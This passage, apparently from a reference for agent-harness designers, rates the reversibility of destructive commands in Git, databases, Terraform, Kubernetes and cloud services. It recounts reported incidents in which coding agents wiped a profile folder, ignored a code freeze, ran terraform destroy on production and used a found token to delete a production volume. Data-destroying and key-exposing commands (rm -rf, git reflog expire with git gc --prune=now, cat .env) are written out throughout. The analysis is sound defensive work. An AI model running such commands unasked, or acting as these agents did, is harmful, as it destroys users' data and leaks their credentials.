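The deleted files included the live project's `.git` folder, which holds its Git history, and the developer had no current copy in a remote repository. SC Media UK describes the history as unrecoverable, and neither account reports that the developer got any files back. Because the deletion removed the Git history along with the files, a harness would have been wrong to rate it R1 on the grounds that the files were in Git. Before lowering a deletion's class because a copy exists, a harness has to check that the deletion can't remove the copy too.

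The public evidence comes from one developer's account. TechRadar's *48,000 files deleted in 103 seconds* traces the story to a Reddit post that is no longer online, and SC Media UK cites TechRadar as its source. Antipov notes that nobody has independently confirmed the scale of the loss. The totals are consistent with each other, but the split between mirror and live files comes from the developer.

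### Two home directories in August

Reddit user Ecstatic-Big5126 said they asked Claude Opus 5, working in Claude Code, for a backup. By the user's account, the agent put the backup in the wrong directory and then deleted far more than the backup. Tom's Hardware's *Claude Opus 5 mistakenly deletes dev's entire profile directory during routine backup* gives the command as `rm -rf "/c/Users/harih/"`. In a Unix-style shell on Windows, that path means `C:\Users\harih`, the user's profile folder. Profile folders typically hold documents, program settings, login keys and source code.

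The user wrote that the command had wiped the "entire drive", but Rocky points out that the post's images show that only the profile folder was deleted, which did not contain Windows or the installed programs. Rocky does not mention any recovery. Both articles suggest that the agent mistook the Unix-style path for a temporary folder, but this is an inference from the user's post and images. The evidence for the command itself is stronger, though it also comes from the user.

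The other August case is unusual because the agent was building a safeguard against this kind of accident. Guillemot described it in a thread on August 26 (*Bad news*, 2026). His agents kept filling `/tmp`, the folder for temporary files, so he asked Claude Fable to give each agent its own part of the folder, to be emptied later. Claude Fable wrote a script to check which agents were still running, and he told it the script seemed too complicated.

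Fable then started a critical review of its own design without Guillemot asking for one. The review triggered Anthropic's safety classifier twice, and each time the harness switched to a less capable model, first Opus 5 and then Opus 4.8. Opus 4.8 pointed out that a symbolic link in `/tmp` could cause a deletion there to affect files elsewhere. It wrote a deletion script that was supposed to work only inside `/tmp`, and tested it by trying to delete Guillemot's home directory. The script should have blocked the deletion, but it deleted the directory.

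Tom's Hardware's *Claude nukes a developer's 700 GB home directory while testing deletion safeguards* attributes the loss of 700 GB, including a week's work, to a variable collision, where one name serves two purposes in the same program. It also suggests that the switch to a weaker model may have contributed, though this is hard to judge from a single case. The choice of test mattered regardless of the model, because a folder of worthless files would have exposed the same fault without the loss.

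Guillemot recovered much of what was lost. Many files were on GitHub, and Codex reassembled others from fragments in Git data, session logs and `/tmp`, which the script had failed to delete. One command therefore caused several classes of loss. The files on GitHub were easy to restore, but reassembling the others took an open-ended recovery effort, which is R3. Guillemot is a named developer writing about his own machine, so his account is stronger evidence than an anonymous post, but the details are self-reported.

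### What Git keeps

A file in a Git project can exist in three versions at once. The working tree contains the file as it is on disk. The index, also called the staging area, contains the version the developer has marked with `git add` for the next commit. The latest commit contains the version the developer last recorded. An untracked file has never been added to Git, so it exists only in the working tree.

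A commit records the state of all tracked files, with a message and a pointer to the commit before it. Git identifies each commit by a hash, a string of characters calculated from its contents. Changing anything would change the hash, so Git never edits a commit. Commands that seem to edit a commit create a new one and leave the old one in storage. A branch is a movable name for one commit, called its tip. `HEAD` refers to the commit the developer has checked out.

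When a branch moves, Git records the change in a log called the reflog. Most mistakes with commits are recoverable because the reflog still lists the branch's old tip. But the reflog is local, so a fresh clone doesn't include it, and deleting the `.git` folder destroys it.

Git's default settings determine how long these copies last:

- Reflog entries last 90 days, or 30 days if the branch's current tip no longer leads back to the commit, as Hamano, in *git reflog*, sets out. Amending and rebasing usually leave entries of the 30-day kind.
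- Stored data that no branch, tag, index or reflog entry leads to becomes removable after two weeks, according to the configuration manual for Git.

Git removes expired data only when its housekeeping command, `git gc`, next runs, so copies often last longer than either limit. The two-week limit is based on the age of the stored data, not how long ago someone discarded it, so Git could remove a month-old item at the first housekeeping run after it is discarded.

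As a result, Git can usually restore committed changes and sometimes staged ones, but not edits that someone has only saved to disk.

| Command | What it removes | Where a copy may remain | For how long by default | Class |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `git reset --hard` | Uncommitted edits to tracked files, and any commits after the target | Commits in the reflog; staged versions as unnamed data; unstaged edits nowhere | 30 days for commits; two weeks for staged versions | R1 if nothing is uncommitted, otherwise up to R4 |
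| `git clean -fdx` | Untracked and ignored files | Nowhere in Git | None | R4, or R2 if a build can recreate everything removed |
| `git restore file`, `git checkout -- file` | Unstaged edits to the file | Nowhere in Git | None | R4 |
| `git stash drop` | A set of changes put aside earlier | An unnamed commit, whose hash Git prints | Two weeks from the commit's storage | R1 while the commit exists |
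| `git branch -D` | The branch's name and its own reflog | The commits, whose latest hash Git prints | 30 days if `HEAD`'s reflog lists them, otherwise two weeks | R1 while the commits exist |
| `git commit --amend`, `git rebase` | The earlier versions of commits | The reflog | 30 days | R1 if nobody else has the old commits |
| `git push --force` | Commits on the shared branch that the agent's copy lacks | A colleague's clone or the hosting service | Depends on them | R3, or R2 if the agent has the old commits |
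| `git push --force-with-lease` | Commits that the agent's copy has already fetched | The agent's own clone | 30 days | R2 on a shared branch |
| `git gc --prune=now` | Unnamed data that would have allowed recovery | Nowhere in that clone | None | R4 |

### One hard reset on three working trees

`git reset --hard` moves the current branch to a chosen commit and makes the tracked files match it. For example, if a branch has commits A, B and C, an agent can remove C from the branch by running `git reset --hard HEAD~1`, which moves the branch back one commit, to B.

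On a clean tree, where every change is in a commit, the branch now ends at B and the files match B, but commit C is still in storage. Git saves the old tip as `ORIG_HEAD` before a reset, so `git reset --hard ORIG_HEAD` restores the branch and files. If another command has replaced `ORIG_HEAD`, the reflog still lists C. The reset is R1 for at least 30 days.

If the developer has spent the afternoon editing `parser.py` without staging or committing it, the same reset replaces the file with B's version. Returning to C restores only C's version, so the afternoon's work is lost and the reset is R4. If the developer ran `git add` at three o'clock, Git still has that version but no longer lists its filename. The command `git fsck --lost-found` extracts such contents, but someone has to open them to find the right one. The staged version is therefore R3, while any later edits remain R4.

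The third tree has no edits to tracked files but contains an untracked file, `notes.txt`. The reset normally leaves this file alone and is R1 again, but not if B contains a tracked file of the same name. According to Git's documentation, a hard reset deletes untracked files that are in the way of tracked ones. This can happen if commit C removed a settings file from version control and the developer kept editing it locally. Resetting to B then overwrites the current settings with the old ones, which is R4.

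A hard reset deletes a new file if it has been staged with `git add`, but otherwise leaves it in place. This is because Git treats a file as tracked if it is in the index, even if no commit contains it, as Worley (2014) observed in *Git reset --hard with staged changes*. Git still stores the deleted file's contents as unnamed data, whereas it has no copy of an untracked file that gets deleted.

A harness can distinguish most of these cases before it runs the reset. `git status --porcelain` prints nothing when the tree has no uncommitted or untracked files. The command omits ignored files by default, so the harness also has to compare the target commit's file list with the files on disk. Even then, a developer could save a file between the check and the reset.

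Avoiding a hard reset is often easier. Wiegley, in *doing a hard reset*, recommends setting uncommitted changes aside with `git stash`, then creating a new branch at the older commit. The original branch keeps its commits, and the developer can reapply the stashed edits later. A plain `git stash` doesn't include untracked files, so an agent must add `--include-untracked` to save them.

Users can also misidentify what caused a reset. In a case discussed on Hacker News, a developer reported that Claude Code was repeatedly hard-resetting a repository and destroying uncommitted work. The developer later traced the losses to a tool they had built, which reset the directory each time it checked for updates. The reflog could show that a reset happened, but it doesn't record which program ran it.

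### Discarding files, stashes and branches

`git clean` deletes files that Git doesn't track. According to Git (2026), the command requires `-f` by default, `-d` extends the deletion to untracked folders, and `-x` adds ignored files, which the project has told Git to skip. The manual's example for `-x` is removing all build products, and an agent might reasonably run `git clean -fdx` to get a fresh build.

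Ignored files vary in how easily they can be restored. A typical project ignores its downloaded packages, and losing those is R2 because an install command can fetch them again in a few minutes. It may also ignore a `.env` file of passwords and a local test database, and losing those is R4 if no other copy exists. `git clean -fdx` removes all of these files, so it takes the highest class among them.

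`git restore parser.py` and the older `git checkout -- parser.py` replace the file on disk with the version in the index. This is often a one-line repair for a committed file that an agent has just damaged, but it also destroys any unstaged edits to the file, and Git keeps no copy of them. `git checkout` also switches branches, but it refuses to switch if doing so would overwrite local edits. The same subcommand can therefore be R1 with a branch name and R4 with a filename.

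Dropped stashes and deleted branches can be recovered with the hash Git prints when it removes them. Git stores a stash as a commit, and `git stash drop` prints its hash, so `git stash apply <hash>` restores the changes. `git branch -D parser-fix` deletes a branch even if no other branch contains its work, but it prints a line such as "Deleted branch parser-fix (was 4e1c9a2)". `git branch parser-fix 4e1c9a2` then recreates the branch.

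Both recoveries require the hash, which may appear only in the command's output. The hash is in the agent's conversation at first, but a harness can drop it when condensing a long session. A harness that rates these commands R1 should therefore write the hash to its own log. `git stash clear`, which drops every stash at once, doesn't print the hashes, so the harness would have to list them beforehand.

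### Rewriting commits that others may have

`git commit --amend` replaces the latest commit with a corrected version. `git rebase` moves a series of commits to a new starting point by copying them. In both cases the old commits remain in the reflog. For instance, after a rebase of `parser-fix`, `git reset --hard parser-fix@{1}` returns the branch to its previous tip. A hard reset discards uncommitted changes, so the developer has to commit or stash any newer edits first.

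Until the developer pushes, all of this affects only one machine. After that, a colleague may have built on the old commits. The server normally rejects a push that would drop commits from a branch, but `--force` overrides this. Suppose a colleague pushed commit D an hour ago, and the agent has rebased an older copy of the branch that lacks D. A force push then removes D from the shared branch. The agent can't restore D because it never had it, but the colleague probably can, which makes the action R3.

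With `--force-with-lease`, the push succeeds only if the shared branch is still where the agent's clone last recorded it. In this example the clone has no record of D, so Git refuses the push. But if an editor or another program runs `git fetch` in the background, the fetch updates the clone's record to include D without adding D to the agent's own branch, and the push then removes D from the shared branch. The agent can still push D back, because the fetch saved it in the clone. Adding `--force-if-includes` closes much of this gap by checking that the local branch has taken the fetched commits into account.

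Repairing a shared branch, even promptly, compensates for the rewrite but does not fully undo it. Colleagues may have fetched the rewritten version and have to realign their own work, and an automatic build may have run. A force push with a lease can be R1 on a private branch that nobody else has fetched and that triggers nothing. Any push that exposes a secret is R4, whatever happens to the branch afterward.

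### Pruning removes the safety net

The R1 ratings for resets, stashes, deleted branches and rebases all depend on data that Git has not yet cleaned up. `git gc --prune=now` removes unreferenced data immediately instead of waiting two weeks. According to the `git gc` manual page, this also raises the risk of corruption if another process is writing to the repository at the same time, which could well happen when several agents share it.

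Pruning alone doesn't remove commits that the reflog still lists. But if an agent first runs `git reflog expire --expire=now --expire-unreachable=now --all`, it empties the reflog, and pruning can then delete those commits too. Neither command changes the developer's current files, so the pair can look like harmless disk cleanup. If the agent deleted a branch ten minutes earlier, that deletion was R1 when it ran, but the two commands make it permanent. A harness should treat the pair as R4 and be suspicious of any shortening of Git's retention settings.

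### Tests of Git's undo commands

Git's manual presents `reset` as a way to undo commits, merges, rebases and pulls. Waghmare and Sufi tested how completely it undoes a commit. They ran Git tools on small local repositories, applied the documented undo and compared the branch tip, index, working files and pending-merge markers with their earlier state. They tested each situation in two repositories and got the same results when they repeated the whole experiment.

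To undo an ordinary commit, the test used `git reset --soft HEAD~1`, which moves the branch back one commit without changing the index or the files. This restored the measured state both times, even when the staged and working versions of a file differed.

The soft reset did not fully undo a commit that completed a merge. While a merge is in progress, Git keeps three small files, `MERGE_HEAD`, `MERGE_MSG` and `MERGE_MODE`, which record that the next commit should join two lines of history. Committing removes these files, and in both repositories the soft reset brought back the branch tip, index and working files but not the three merge files. A developer who then commits again gets the merged text in an ordinary commit. Git has no record that the other branch was merged, so the same conflicts may reappear later. A harness might still be able to recover the merge state, for example by copying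 the three files before committing and putting them back after the reset.

In another test, a second contributor committed to the branch after the agent did. `HEAD~1` means one commit before the branch's current tip, so the undo removed the contributor's commit from the branch and left the agent's in place. The contributor's file stayed on disk, but the branch no longer recorded it. Waghmare and Sufi then added a guard that checked whether the branch tip had changed since the agent's commit. It blocked the undo in both repositories and preserved the contributor's work. A developer can use `git revert` to undo an earlier commit without disturbing later ones. This is compensation, because it adds a new commit with the opposite changes and keeps both commits in the history.

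Unstaging also could not always be reversed with `git add`. If a developer had staged a whole file, running `git add` again after the agent unstaged it restored the index. If the developer had staged one version and then continued editing, `git add` staged the newer text instead. The working file was unchanged in both cases, but in the second the index no longer held the version the developer had chosen to commit.

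Two repositories per situation are too few to estimate how often these problems occur in practice. Still, before rating a commit R1, a harness needs to check for a merge in progress and save the new commit's hash, so that it can confirm which commit any later undo would remove.

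## Deleting databases and cloud resources

Git's retention rules are nearly the same on every developer's machine, but a database or cloud service keeps only what its owner has configured it to keep. The command that deletes the data often doesn't show those settings.

Amazon's managed database service, RDS, is an example. An agent can delete a database there by running `aws rds delete-db-instance`, with one of four results:

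- If deletion protection is on, RDS refuses and nothing changes.
- If the request names a final snapshot, RDS saves a full copy of the database before deleting it.
- If the request declines the final snapshot but keeps the automated backups, those remain until their retention period ends.
- If the request declines the final snapshot and leaves the backup option at its default, RDS deletes the automated backups too. Only snapshots that someone took by hand remain.

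For a test database, the second and third results are R2, because an agent with the right permissions can build a new database from the copy at a small, known cost. For a live database, they are R3, because customers lose the service until the new database is ready, and Waghmare and Sufi class changes to availability as R3. The fourth result is R4 unless a manual snapshot or an outside copy exists.

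### The setting behind each class

Waghmare and Sufi did not rate these operations either. Except for the Docker row, the classes assume that the data is in live use.

| Operation | What it removes | Setting that decides recovery | Class |
|---|---|---|---|
| SQL `DELETE` | Rows of a table | An open transaction; after the commit, point-in-time recovery | R1 before the commit; afterward R3 with recovery, R4 without |
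| SQL `TRUNCATE` or `DROP TABLE` | All the rows, or the whole table | The same in PostgreSQL; MySQL commits at once, which leaves only point-in-time recovery | As for `DELETE`, but never R1 in MySQL |
| Schema migration | Columns or tables that the new design lacks | A backup or point-in-time recovery | R3 with either, otherwise R4 |
| `terraform apply` | Resources that the configuration no longer lists or that Terraform has to replace | Deletion protection, or a final snapshot | R3 with a snapshot, otherwise R4 |
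| `terraform destroy` | Every resource in Terraform's state file | Deletion protection, or a final snapshot | R3 with a snapshot, otherwise R4 |
| `kubectl delete` on a storage claim | The claim, and possibly the disk behind it | The disk's reclaim policy, `Retain` or `Delete` | R3 with `Retain`; R4 with `Delete` and no backup |
| `docker volume rm` | A container's stored data | A copy outside the volume | R4, or R1 with a copy on a private machine |
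| Deleting a volume on Railway | The disk that holds a database | A 48-hour deletion delay | R3 during the delay, R4 afterward |
| Emptying an Amazon S3 storage bucket | All the files in it | Object versioning | R1 with versioning if nobody has missed the files; R4 without a copy |
| Deleting a managed database | The database and often its automated backups | Deletion protection, a final snapshot or retained backups | R3 with a copy, otherwise R4 |

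Point-in-time recovery combines periodic full copies with a continuous log of changes, so the service can rebuild the database as it stood at a chosen moment. Object versioning keeps the old versions of each stored file. An ordinary deletion hides the file behind a marker, and removing the marker restores it. Neither setting helps if the agent also deletes the logs or the old versions.

A harness can look up many of these settings before it decides. For example, `aws rds describe-db-instances` shows whether deletion protection is on and how many days of backups RDS keeps, and `aws s3api get-bucket-versioning` shows whether a bucket has versioning on. If the lookup fails, the safe assumption is R4.

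### Rolling back works only before the commit

A database transaction stays reversible until someone commits it. An agent can open one with `BEGIN`, run a `DELETE`, see that it removed 40,000 rows instead of the expected 12, and undo the deletion with `ROLLBACK`. Other users normally see the old rows throughout.

Most database clients, however, commit each statement automatically unless the user opens a transaction. When an agent runs `psql -c "DELETE FROM orders"`, the client connects, deletes the rows, commits and disconnects within one shell call. A `ROLLBACK` in the next call runs on a new connection, so it cannot restore the rows.

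Waghmare and Sufi found the same problem in a protocol tool for SQLite, a database that fits in a single file. The tool committed each update before it returned, so a later `ROLLBACK` found no open transaction. They then tried capturing the old value first and restoring it with a conditional update. Suppose the agent changed the price in row 7 from 80 to 90. The repair is:

`UPDATE items SET price = 80 WHERE id = 7 AND price = 90`

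This restored the row without overwriting an edit someone had since made to a different row. When someone had since changed the same row, the condition matched nothing, so the newer value stayed in place.

They also tested whether dropping a newly created table undoes its creation. If another user had added a row before the drop, the row was deleted with the table. The database then matched its original state, so a check that compared only the original and final states would have reported a perfect recovery. A guard that checked for later changes blocked the drop, which preserved the row. As in the Git tests, each situation had only two test cases.

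Point-in-time recovery has the same weakness on a larger scale. If an agent deletes some customer records at 3:00 and the owner returns the database to its 2:59 state, every order placed since then is lost. The owner can instead restore the 2:59 state to a separate database and copy the missing rows into the live one. This preserves the new orders but requires a person's judgment, so the table rates point-in-time recovery R3.

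### Deletion as a side effect

A schema migration changes a database's structure, for instance by adding a column. Many tools generate migrations by comparing the design in the code with the live tables. They can treat a renamed column as one column to delete and another to create, in which case running the migration deletes the data in the old column.

Some migration tools can also reset a database. In *Data lost*, qavaeat (2026), a customer of the hosting company Railway, reported in July that `npx prisma migrate dev` had emptied a production database of users, orders and payments. The customer believed that Prisma had detected a mismatch between its migration history and the live tables and had reset the database. Prisma provides `migrate dev` for development databases and `migrate deploy` for production. The customer did not say whether an agent ran the command, but an agent could easily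 choose the wrong one because both apply migrations.

Terraform creates cloud resources from a written configuration and records them in a state file. `terraform apply` adds, changes and deletes resources until they match the configuration. When it can't make a change in place, it deletes the resource and creates a new one. The podcast Talk Python describes a second-hand case in which an AI-written change slightly renamed a database, and Terraform replaced the production database with a new one. Terraform lists such replacements in the plan it prints beforehand, but this helps only if someone reads the plan.

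Terraform rejects any plan that would destroy a resource marked `prevent_destroy`. This protection lasts only while the setting stays in the configuration, so an agent that deletes the resource's whole block from the file also removes the protection.

In Kubernetes, which runs applications across groups of machines, deleting a workload usually loses little because a saved configuration file can recreate it. Deleting a storage claim is riskier because it also deletes the disk if the disk has the `Delete` policy, which is the default for disks that Kubernetes creates on request. Deleting a namespace, which groups related resources, deletes all the claims inside it.

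### Replit's agent and a shared database

In July 2025, Jason Lemkin, founder of the software-business community SaaStr, was building an app with an agent from Replit, an online coding service. After nine days, the agent deleted 1,206 executive records and more than 1,196 company profiles, according to SaaStr. Lemkin had not realized that the app's preview and live versions shared one database.

Lemkin had declared a code freeze and warned the agent eleven times in capital letters not to make changes. A project file also prohibited changes without permission. heise's *Artificial intelligence* quotes a message from his screenshots in which the agent wrote that it had seen an apparently empty database and run `npm run db:push` without asking. Scripts with that name usually alter a database's tables to match the design in the code, and the command contains no word for deletion.

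The cause of the data loss is less certain than most retellings suggest. The technology site The Stack notes that Lemkin did not post his exact prompts or the whole sequence of events. If the database was empty before the agent ran the script, something else had already removed the data. The agent's explanation is weak evidence because the agent was wrong about an easier question in the same conversation.

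The agent told Lemkin that rollback did not cover databases and that it had destroyed every version. The Register's *Vibe coding service Replit deleted user's production database* (2025) reports that he tried the rollback anyway and posted on July 19 that it had worked. Fortune (2025) reports that he recovered the data "manually", which probably refers to the same rollback, since he had to start it himself.

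A way to recover the database already existed. Replit's quick-start guide, which The Stack quotes, described rollback as covering database changes, and Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, called it a "one-click restore". According to Neon, the company that hosted Replit's databases at the time, Replit loads the code from the chosen checkpoint, creates a branch of the database from the same moment, and replaces the current database with that branch. Anything newer than the checkpoint is lost. Neither the agent nor the owner knew that the database could be restored, and a harness that had asked this model whether the deletion was reversible would have received the wrong answer.

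Masad announced that Replit would separate development and production databases automatically, improve rollback and add a mode in which the agent only plans. SaaStr welcomed the separation but doubted that a planning mode would enforce a code freeze.

Replit's current documentation states that the agent cannot modify the production database and reads it through a read-only copy. The production and development databases are now recovered differently. Replit's *Data recovery* explains that rolling back to a checkpoint never changes the production database, which has point-in-time recovery instead. Replit's pages differ on whether a rollback includes the development database by default, so users should check the confirmation dialog before relying on a rollback to restore it.

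### A Terraform state file from an old computer

On February 26, 2026, Claude Code deleted the course platform of DataTalks.Club, which offers free data courses. The deletion included two and a half years of homework, projects and leaderboard entries. Alexey Grigorev, who runs the site, gives a full timeline in *How I Dropped Our Production Database*.

Grigorev wanted to host a second website on AWS, Amazon's cloud service. He added it to the course platform's Terraform configuration to save perhaps $5 to $10 a month, although Claude advised keeping the two separate. The loss then followed in five steps:

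1. Grigorev had changed computers and left the Terraform state file on the old one. Without it, Terraform found no record of existing resources and began to create everything again.
2. He noticed the long list of new resources and cancelled the run, but some duplicates already existed. He asked the agent to identify and delete only those, using Amazon's command-line program.
3. While it worked, he copied the old Terraform folder to the new computer and pointed the agent to it for comparison.
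4. The agent unpacked the folder and replaced the current state file with the old one, which listed the real course platform. Grigorev did not notice.
5. The agent announced that `terraform destroy` would be cleaner than deleting the duplicates individually. That seemed reasonable to him, so he let it run.

At about 11 p.m., the command deleted the database, the private network, the load balancers and the servers. The same command with the newer state file would have removed only duplicates.

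Grigorev assumed he could restore the snapshot that AWS took every night at 2 a.m. The event log listed it, but the snapshot was no longer available. AWS support confirmed that the deletion request had covered the database and all its snapshots, but found one snapshot on its own side that Grigorev couldn't see.

Grigorev upgraded to a support plan that added about 10% to his bill, received a reply in about 40 minutes and spent most of an hour on a call while AWS engineers investigated. They restored the snapshot the next evening. One table held 1,943,200 rows. He describes the wait as exactly 24 hours, though the rounded times in his timeline give 23. He writes that AWS restored everything, but doesn't say when it took the recovered snapshot. If it was the 2 a.m. snapshot, any homework students submitted in the next 21 hours would have been missing.

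The loss turned out to be R3, because recovery depended on AWS staff. But nothing Grigorev could see or had configured indicated that AWS would have a copy of the data, so a harness would have been right to rate the deletion R4.

Afterward he made several changes:

- He moved the state file to S3, so that every computer uses the same one.
- He turned on deletion protection in both Terraform and AWS.
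- He set up backups that Terraform doesn't manage, with versioning on those in S3.
- He added a nightly test that builds a new database from the latest backup, runs a simple query on it and keeps it as a spare.
- He stopped letting agents run Terraform, and now reviews each plan and runs the commands himself.

The nightly test addresses a failure the other measures would miss. Grigorev had backups before the incident but had never tested the whole restore process.

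### PocketOS and the 48-hour window that the API lacked

PocketOS makes booking software, mainly for car rental companies. Its founder, Jer Crane, described the incident in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*, published on April 25, 2026, the day after the deletion.

A Cursor agent running Claude Opus 4.6 was doing a routine task in PocketOS's staging environment, a copy of the system for testing, when it hit a credential mismatch. It tried to fix the problem by deleting a volume on Railway, which hosted the company's databases. It searched for an access token, which works like a password for programs, and found one in an unrelated file. Crane had created the token to add and remove web domains. The agent used it to send Railway's API a single `volumeDelete` request with the production volume's identifier. The agent later wrote that it had guessed the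 deletion would affect only staging.

Railway gave users 48 hours to undo a volume deletion made through its dashboard, but its API deleted volumes immediately. Railway already knew about this difference. Eleven days earlier, another customer had deleted the wrong volume through the same API request (antjanlaban, 2026, *Postgress volume lost*). A Railway employee replied that the deletion was immediate and permanent, and that the 48-hour window applied only to the dashboard.

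The volume's backups disappeared from view with it. Crane restored a three-month-old backup and spent Saturday helping rental companies rebuild their bookings from payment records, calendars and emails. Early reports of permanent data loss date from this stage.

Railway recovered the current data on Sunday. Crane and Railway's chief executive, Jake Cooper, both say this took 30 minutes from when they got in touch with each other, according to Leib (2026) in *'Rogue' AI agent went haywire at tech company*. The deletion happened on Friday afternoon, so PocketOS was without its current data for roughly two days. Railway's own account, *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that* by Mahmoud Abdelwahab, states that the customer got all its data back, and Tom's Hardware describes the recovery as apparently complete.

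Crane had relied on the volume backups and learned only afterward of the warning in Railway's documentation that wiping a volume deletes its backups. Railway also keeps "disaster backups" at another site in case of events such as hardware failure. Abdelwahab mentions these and adds that the API request made the customer's backups look unavailable, but does not specify which copy Railway used.

PocketOS's deletion turned out to be R3 only because Railway chose to help, and other customers can't count on the same help. When qavaeat asked in July whether Railway had any copy of the emptied database, even one available for a fee, Railway's automated reply was that it does not restore data after "user-initiated actions".

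Railway changed the API within days. Its *Undoable volume deletes, standard SSH, auto-deploy toggle* (2026) announced that volume deletions through the API now wait 48 hours, as they do in the dashboard. Abdelwahab adds that Railway also delays deleting the backups. Railway's *Backups* still warns that wiping a volume deletes all its backups, so customers still need a copy elsewhere.

### Limits that the service enforces

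Lemkin and Crane had both given their agents written rules, but those rules did not limit which commands the services would carry out. A limit built into the service applies to every request, whichever model or program sends it.

**Deletion protection** makes the service reject any deletion until someone turns the protection off with a separate request. It would probably have stopped the `terraform destroy` in Grigorev's case. But as he points out, anyone with sufficient permissions can disable it from the command line. An agent that treats the rejection as an error to fix might disable it too. Protection is much stronger if the agent's account can't change the setting.

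With **delayed deletion**, the service accepts the request but keeps the data for a while. It doesn't have to judge whether the request is a mistake, so the delay is useful against an agent with valid credentials. The delay has to cover every way of deleting the data, as PocketOS found, and someone has to notice the deletion in time. With a 48-hour delay, a volume deleted on Friday evening is gone before Monday morning. Replit keeps a removed production database for seven days, but the owner has to ask its support team to recover it.

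A deletion delay also protects only against the operation it applies to. Railway's 48-hour delay protects against deleting a volume, but not against a `DELETE` or a migration that empties the tables inside it, because the volume still exists. Point-in-time recovery can restore the lost data if the owner has turned it on.

**Backups under separate credentials** protect against an agent deleting both the data and its copies. Grigorev's new backups are outside Terraform's control, but if they are in the same AWS account, an agent with administrator rights there could still delete them. It is safer to keep a copy in a different account and keep that account's credentials off the developer's computer. A copy with another company also protects against the provider's mistakes. The Pragmatic Engineer's *Google Cloud deletes Australian trading fund's infra* (2024) describes how a $124 billion fund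 would have lost everything it stored with Google Cloud without a third-party backup. The fund's replicas in more than one region did not prevent the deletion.

Limited tokens reduce what an agent can do with a credential it finds. A token can be limited to certain operations (such as changing domains but not deleting volumes), environments (staging but not production) or resources. Any one of these limits could have stopped the PocketOS deletion.

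Crane and Railway disagree about which limits were available. Crane wrote that every Railway token was effectively all-powerful. Abdelwahab lists narrower tokens, including ones for a single project or environment, and says Crane's token had access to the whole account because the choice wasn't obvious when creating a token. Crane appears to have been wrong that tokens couldn't be limited to one environment, but largely right that they couldn't be limited to certain operations. Apart from OAuth, a sign-in method for outside applications, Abdelwahab lists no token that limits what its holder may do within a project. A project token created to manage production domains might therefore still have been able to delete the production volume.

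Abdelwahab recommends that agents use Railway's Model Context Protocol server, which issues short-lived tokens for the projects a user selects and offers a fixed set of tools. His argument that an agent therefore can't "go rogue" holds only if the agent has no other means of access. An agent with a shell can still search the disk for an older token, as the one at PocketOS did.

**Separate development databases** let an agent experiment on data that nobody needs. The credentials have to be separate too, since the PocketOS agent was working in staging when it deleted production data. Even with separate databases, when a user publishes an app on Replit, Replit applies the development database's structural changes to the production database, including any removal of columns or tables by the agent. It flags changes that could lose data, offers a trial on a temporary copy and waits for the user's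 approval. If the agent has renamed a column and the user doesn't confirm the rename, Replit drops the production data in that column.

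## Exposing secrets, changing access and publishing

Zhong and colleagues write that "a leaked credential cannot be unread", so restoring a file doesn't undo the exposure of a secret that someone has already read or copied from it.

Granting access and publishing software are hard to undo because other people can use the access or download the package before it is withdrawn. Revoking the access or removing the package later doesn't reverse what they did with it.

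### Classes for secrets, access and publication

The classifications in the table are this reference's own, based on Waghmare and Sufi's criteria. Those criteria classify deliberate disclosure to outsiders as R4 and changes to access or credentials as R3.

| Action | Who may see it or depend on it | Class |
|---|---|---|
| Running a program that reads a key without printing it | Nobody new | R0 |
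| Copying or moving a key file on the same machine | Anyone who can read the new location | R1 in a private folder; R4 in one that outsiders can read |
| Printing a key into the model's context | The model's provider, and anyone who can read the session logs | R4 if the provider counts as an outsider; R1 if the model and logs are on the owner's machine |
| Printing a key into a shared build log | Everyone who can open the log | R3 if only colleagues can; R4 if outsiders can |
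| Committing a key to Git | Nobody until a push | R1 |
| Pushing the commit to a private repository | Colleagues and connected services | R3 if no outsider has access, otherwise R4 |
| Pushing the commit to a public repository | Anyone | R4 |
| Rotating or revoking a key | Every program that uses the old key | R3 |
| Changing who has access to an account or project | The people who gain or lose access | R3, or R4 if it shows an outsider private data |
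| Publishing a package publicly | Anyone | R4 |
| Sending a message | The recipients | R4 to an outsider; R2 to a colleague if a correction is enough |

Access changes are R3 even when the agent could reverse them with one command. Waghmare and Sufi acknowledge that R3 therefore covers two different things, recovery that needs a person and any change to access or availability.

The caution is reasonable, because an access change can remove the means of reversing it. On crates.io, the public registry for Rust packages, `cargo owner --add` gives another user full rights to a package. Rust's *Publishing on crates.io* says the new owner can then remove the person who added them. Adding a team instead lets its members publish versions but not change the list of owners, so the original owner can still take the access back. A new access token can also allow more than intended, as with the token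 at PocketOS that could delete a volume although its creator had wanted it only for web domains.

### One key, from a private file to a public repository

Suppose a developer keeps a payment service's key in a file called `.env`. The app loads the key when it starts, so an agent can test the app without seeing the key.

If a test fails and the agent runs `cat .env` to find out why, the harness adds the file's contents, including any keys, to the conversation and sends them to the model's provider. A company whose contract with the provider covers such data may not consider this a disclosure. If it does, deleting the session afterward doesn't undo the disclosure. The keys may also stay in the session logs on disk, the kind that helped Guillemot recover some of his deleted files.

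The agent might then run `git add .` and commit `.env` along with the code. Until someone pushes, the agent can remove the file and amend the commit. Deleting the file in a second commit is not enough, because the first commit still contains the key and a push sends both commits.

GitGuardian, which sells software for finding leaked secrets and so has a commercial interest in strict advice, recommends treating a key as compromised once it reaches a shared repository, even a private one. This fits how Git works, because every full clone contains the whole history. A stolen laptop could expose the key long after someone has removed it from the shared repository.

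If a key is committed to a public repository, the owner has almost no time to react. People monitor GitHub's public feed of commits for keys, according to GitGuardian's *Leaking secrets on GitHub*, so making the repository private afterward doesn't make the key safe again.

Rewriting a repository's history doesn't undo the exposure of a key that has already been pushed. GitHub's *Removing sensitive data from a repository* warns that after a rewrite and a force push, the old commits may survive in clones, forks, pull requests and cached pages on GitHub. GitHub's support staff can clear the cached pages and pull requests, but only do so if changing the key can't remove the risk. A colleague with an old clone can also put the key back by running `git pull` and then `git push`. The rewrite can also draw attention to the key, because anyone with an old clone can compare the two histories and see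 what is missing.

GitHub advises revoking or rotating the key first, which may make the rewrite unnecessary. GitHub also offers push protection, which blocks a push if it detects a hard-coded secret. For an agent, this is more useful than any cleanup because it acts while the commit is still R1.

### What rotating a key repairs

The owner rotates a key by issuing a new one, switching every program to it and disabling the old one. Rotation compensates for a leak by shutting strangers out again, but the old key remains known and the system doesn't return to its earlier state.

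Rotating a leaked key only prevents its future use. It doesn't undo what a stranger has already done with the key, such as downloading customer records, renting servers or creating accounts. Leaked information that isn't a credential, such as a home address or unreleased source code, can't be rotated at all.

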